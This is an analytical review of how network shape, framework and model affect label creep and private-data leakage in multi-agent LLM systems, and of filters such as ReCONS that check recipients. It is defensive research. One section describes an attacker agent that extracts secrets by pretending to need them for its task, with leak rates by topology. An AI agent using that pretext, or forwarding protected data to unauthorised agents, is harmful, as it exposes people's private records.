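Gregory and colleagues simulated label creep using abstract tasks. Each task is a set of tool calls, some of which need the results of others. The simulation divides the calls among several agents and marks some calls as sensitive. A sensitive call gives its agent a high label. When one agent needs another's result, the result takes the shortest route through the network, and every agent on the way with a lower label than the sender's takes on the sender's label. An agent's label never goes down.

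The loss for a task is

L = (calls that introduce a high label or run under one) / (all calls).

This overstates the blocked work, since a real policy would allow some of those calls. Gregory and colleagues also report the excess loss, the part due to the graph. They calculate it by subtracting the loss for the same task on an ideal graph, which has a direct link between each pair of agents that must exchange a result and no other links.

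With five agents, 20 calls per task and four sensitive calls, the excess loss was about 5 percentage points for a star, 4 for a hierarchy and 3 for a ring. The star has an extra agent as its hub, and the hierarchy has two managers and a supervisor, all of which only pass messages on. A mesh, which links every pair of agents, did as well as the ideal graph because its extra links went unused.

### Two results through one hub

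Suppose agent A looks up a salary and sends it to C, which writes a payslip. Agent B looks up the office's opening hours and sends them to D, which updates the website. Each agent makes one tool call, and only A's is sensitive.

| Route | A | B | C | D | Loss |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Direct links from A to C and B to D | High | Low | High | Low | 2 of 4 |
| Through a hub, A's result first | High | Low | High | High | 3 of 4 |
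| Through a hub, B's result first | High | Low | High | Low | 2 of 4 |

In the second row, the hub takes on the high label from A's salary data. When it forwards the opening hours to D, that message carries the high label too, so the website tool may reject the update even though the hours are public. The excess loss is one call in four, or 25 percentage points.

The graph is the same in the second and third rows, so a diagram of the links can't show the difference. *Higher-Order Aggregate Networks in the Analysis of Temporal Networks* (2015) gives the general rule that *a* can influence *c* through *b* only if *a* and *b* make contact before *b* and *c* do. A's salary data can influence D only if it reaches the hub before the hub writes to D.

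Now suppose someone adds a direct link from B to D after the salary has passed through the hub. Gregory and colleagues didn't simulate a change like this, but their rules determine the result:

- If B hasn't sent the opening hours yet, they take the new link. D stays low, and the loss is 2 of 4.
- If the hub has already delivered them, D has the high label and the new link can't remove it. The loss stays at 3 of 4. If D then makes another call, that one is high as well, which makes 4 of 5 instead of the 2 of 5 that direct links would have given from the start.

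The hub could also avoid the problem by handling the salary in a separate context, as an LLMbda program can with `fork`. *APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) tested this idea with real models. Its agent can start a disposable branch to read restricted data, and reading the data raises only the branch's label. The branch inherits the agent's label, so the agent can't use a branch to shed a label it already has. Like FIDES's quarantined model, the branch can return a value in a fixed form, but the deployer has to decide whether the agent may treat that value as trusted or public.

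On a benchmark of 20 office workflows, the system completed 87 to 89 percent of tasks with the model GPT-5.6 Luna, compared with 56.5 percent without the branches. No attack succeeded in either case, so the benefit of the branches was that more tasks were completed. If the hub in the example used a branch to pass on A's result and then discarded the branch, the hub's label and D's label would both stay low.

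### More links, more agents and grouped tools

Across the graphs that Gregory and colleagues tested, the loss had a rank correlation of −0.96 with density, the share of possible links that exist. Ordering the graphs from sparsest to densest therefore almost exactly orders them from highest loss to lowest. The loss also rose with the average distance between agents, with a correlation of 0.87.

These figures come from only nine graphs, the four standard shapes and five random ones. Denser graphs usually have shorter paths too, and nine graphs are too few to separate the effect of density from that of path length. The star and the hierarchy also don't fit the pattern. With five working agents, the star is denser, with 5 of its 15 possible links compared with 7 of 28 for the hierarchy, but it had the higher loss at four sensitive calls, probably because every routed message passes through the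 same hub.

Spreading the same 20 calls over 20 agents instead of 5 reduced the loss, because each agent's context collected fewer labels. But the excess loss mostly rose in the star, ring and hierarchy, and every shape had more links to monitor. In the mesh, the number of links grew from 10 to 190.

Gregory and colleagues suggest a random graph as a compromise. They report that one generated with a 30 percent chance of each link came close to the mesh, and note that such graphs should need 70 percent fewer links on average. However, they kept only graphs in which every agent could reach every other, and the five-agent graph they tested had 7 of the 10 possible links. The result is therefore weaker evidence for sparse networks than it would be if the tested graph had 70 percent fewer links.

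Grouping sensitive tools also lowered the loss in every shape. A company might give all its financial tools to one banking agent, for example, so that fewer agents pick up high labels from their own calls. But grouping raised the excess loss in the shapes that lack some direct links, because it lowered the loss in the ideal graph even more.

No arrangement eliminated the loss. In the payslip example, C needs the salary, so its call is high on any graph. Reducing the loss further would require declassification.

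### Where private data travels

The simulated agents send only the results a task requires, but real agents often send more. *AgentLeak* (El Yagoubi, Badu-Marfo and Al Mallah, 2026) describes a scheduling agent that gave the user a clean appointment confirmation but put the patient's complete medical record in its message to another agent. In the paper's tests of coordinators with workers, 68.8 percent of runs leaked private data in messages between agents, and 27.2 percent leaked it in the final output.

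That benchmark used one fixed arrangement. Ogundoyin and Ikram (2026), in *When Agents Talk, Secrets Travel*, took 485 of its scenarios and ran each one on six different graphs. They tracked one protected value per scenario, such as a diagnosis, and recorded whether it reached any agent that the larger graph had added. These are the results without an attacker, using the model Qwen3-32B and the framework LangGraph:

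| Graph | Scenarios in which an added agent received the value |
|---|---|
| Two agents (baseline) | 0% |
| Coordinator with six workers | 35.3% |
| Four agents, all linked | 45.6% |
| Seven agents, all linked | 44.1% |
| Ten agents, all linked | 44.7% |
| Hierarchy of seven agents | 49.9% |

With an adversary inside the system, the hierarchy's figure rose to 52.2 percent, which is the top of the range in the paper's summary.

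The baseline figure is zero by construction because the baseline has no added agents. The researchers also left each scenario's release policy unchanged when they enlarged the graph, so an added agent never had permission to receive the value, whatever its job. Enlarging the graph changed who received the data much more than how often it leaked, since the share of scenarios with any unauthorised disclosure stayed between 60.6 and 62.8 percent across all six graphs.

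The results don't support a general ranking of shapes. The hierarchy was the worst on LangGraph, but on AutoGen, another framework, the fully linked graphs were the worst, with rates of up to 37.5 percent compared with 24.7 percent for the hierarchy. The choice of model mattered even more. On the five larger graphs, rates ranged from 57 to 66 percent with GPT-5-mini and from 9 to 12 percent with Gemini 3.7 Flash.

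Part of the difference between the frameworks may come from how they pass information along. In AutoGen, a value travels further only if each agent repeats it in a new message. In the hierarchy, the value reached an added agent in 34.0 percent of AutoGen runs when at least one added agent was one step from the agent that first had it, and in 2.8 percent when every added agent was at least two steps away. LangGraph keeps a shared state that later agents can read, and its corresponding figures were 55.9 and 60.3 percent. Distance therefore gave some protection in AutoGen but none in LangGraph. The simulation's labels, like leaks in LangGraph, don't weaken with distance, so on AutoGen they would often restrict an agent that the secret had never reached.

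A separate experiment compared eight frameworks on the same scenarios with the same model. The protected value appeared without permission in 43.38 percent of recorded events on AutoGen and 0.29 percent on Google ADK. Four frameworks had rates above 20 percent, and the other four had rates below 1 percent. A designer who compares only diagrams of the links would miss these differences between frameworks.

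### An agent that asks for secrets

*Topology Matters* (Liu, Cao and colleagues, 2025) provides the clearest evidence that dense links increase leaks. In its tests, one agent held a private document and another, the attacker, asked for information, claiming to need it for the task. With four agents running on Llama 3.1 70B, the attacker recovered 29.65 percent of the private details in a fully linked graph and 17.47 percent in a tree. In a chain of six agents, it recovered 21.80 percent from its neighbour at the end of the chain but only 1.28 percent when the two agents were at opposite ends.

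Liu and colleagues recommend sparse or hierarchical networks, with agents that hold secrets placed far from agents that might ask for them. Sparser networks leaked less, but this pattern was less regular in models that leaked little. With four agents running on GPT-4o-mini, for example, the tree leaked slightly more than the fully linked graph.

### Checking each recipient

Since neither the graph nor the framework reliably predicts a leak, Ogundoyin and Ikram built a filter called ReCONS that checks messages as agents send them. It works in three steps:

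1. **Detect.** Pattern matching, software that recognises names and similar items, and a language model look for protected values in the message.
2. **Decide.** For each value found, ReCONS checks whether the scenario's policy lets this recipient have it. If so, the value goes through unchanged.
3. **Transform.** Otherwise, ReCONS disguises the value. It encrypts an account number into another string of the same format, replaces a name with a pseudonym, and has a language model rewrite sensitive prose. If these methods fail, it deletes the value.

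The researchers set aside 405 scenarios for the final test and compared ReCONS with blanket redaction, which deletes every protected value it detects.

| | Unauthorised disclosures remaining | Authorised disclosures preserved |
|---|---|---|
| Blanket redaction | 28.3% | 20.5% |
| ReCONS | 29.25% | 94.1% |

Without a filter, 96.7 percent of the unauthorised disclosures went through. ReCONS blocked about as much as blanket redaction while letting through far more of what agents were allowed to share. But the second column is based on only 303 authorised disclosures, and the difference between the two methods comes from ten scenarios.

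Checking the recipient contributed little to this result. Replacing that check with a fixed list of the fields each scenario allowed anyone to receive raised the remaining disclosures only to 29.81 percent, and the filter preserved every authorised disclosure. Most of the advantage over blanket redaction therefore came simply from having a list of permitted fields. The benchmark may understate the value of checking recipients, because few of its scenarios let agents share any protected field.

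Of the 10,116 unauthorised disclosures that got past ReCONS, 95.5 percent were values that it never detected. It did worst on information that is sensitive because of its meaning, such as a legal strategy, and missed or failed to hide 55.7 percent of these cases. Labelling information at its source would avoid this problem but would cause label creep.

ReCONS can identify the receiving agent only for direct messages and reads from shared memory. For the other channels, such as tool calls and saved files, it uses the list of permitted fields. Its use of that list accounted for most of the other disclosures it let through.

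### Looking beyond the next agent

A recipient that is authorised to have a value can still pass it to one that is not. Ogundoyin and Ikram tried to prevent this by blocking a value if the graph contained any path from its recipient to an unauthorised agent. In a small check, this rule blocked 14 of 17 disclosures that the policy allowed. A path shows only that an agent could forward the value, and in many cases it never would.

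*Judging Before Propagation* (Wu, Delattre and Cao, 2026) uses a narrower graph that contains only the exchanges planned for the current task. Before releasing a value from memory, its software checks every planned recipient further along the graph. One version withholds the value if any of those recipients is not allowed to have it. The other releases the value but removes it from messages just before they reach the first forbidden recipient on each path.

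In 144 test cases with four agents each, these checks reduced unauthorised disclosures by 86 to 94 percent compared with checking only the next recipient and what it had already received. The system kept at least 93.6 percent of the accuracy it had with the simpler check. However, the software blocks any message to an agent that the plan doesn't list as a recipient for that sender, and it assumes that the plan stays fixed during the task. Wu and colleagues leave replanning to future work.

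### Dense links or sparse ones

Dense links reduce label creep, but they create more channels to check, more agents that could receive private data, and more ways for a planted instruction to spread. With 20 agents, a star has 20 links and one hub that can mix all the agents' labels. A mesh has no hub, but each agent can send a secret directly to 19 others.

The two experiments disagree partly because they treat spare links differently. In the simulation, a spare link carries nothing, so it can only help. A language model with a spare link may use it to send a colleague the whole patient record. The simulation is therefore a better guide when software controls what agents send, and the leak tests are a better guide when the models decide.

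A designer could allow direct links and send every message through one gateway that checks its label and recipient. The number of links would then matter less than the number of messages. In the payslip example, direct links need two messages and the hub needs four, so the denser graph would need fewer checks. None of these studies tested this combination. Gregory and colleagues, who use the number of links as their measure of security cost, list tests on real agents as future work.

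### If the graph changes during a run

Both main experiments compare fixed graphs, so any conclusion about changes during a run is an inference. In *PiSAs*, Gupta, Mohammadi Sepahvand and colleagues (2026) include a system in which the route is chosen during the run, although the set of agents doesn't change. Each user has an agent, and the active agent chooses which colleague's agent to consult next. They found that dividing data among agents substantially reduced privacy violations, largely because the agents shared less information overall, including information the task needed.

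One way to apply fixed-graph results would be to combine every link that exists at any point in the run into a single graph. *Weisfeiler and Leman Follow the Arrow of Time* (2025) notes that every path that respects the order of contacts also appears in the combined graph, but that some paths in the combined graph do not respect that order. A check on the combined graph would therefore miss no route along the recorded links, but would include some that information could never take, such as from A to D when B's result goes through the hub first. It would also require knowing every link in advance.

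The timing of a change probably matters as much as the change itself. A new direct link can keep later messages away from a contaminated hub, but it can't lower the labels that agents already have. Removing a link doesn't take back what has already crossed it. In tests by Liu and colleagues, most of the details that leaked did so within the first two or three rounds of conversation, so even a brief connection to a hostile agent could be enough to cause a leak.

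An agent that joins midway won't be on any existing list of permitted recipients. If ReCONS treated the new agent like those added in the experiment, it would disguise every protected value it detected in messages to that agent until someone changed the policy. If the new agent got the same data from a saved file, ReCONS would check only whether the field was on the permitted list, so a field meant for another agent could reach the new agent.
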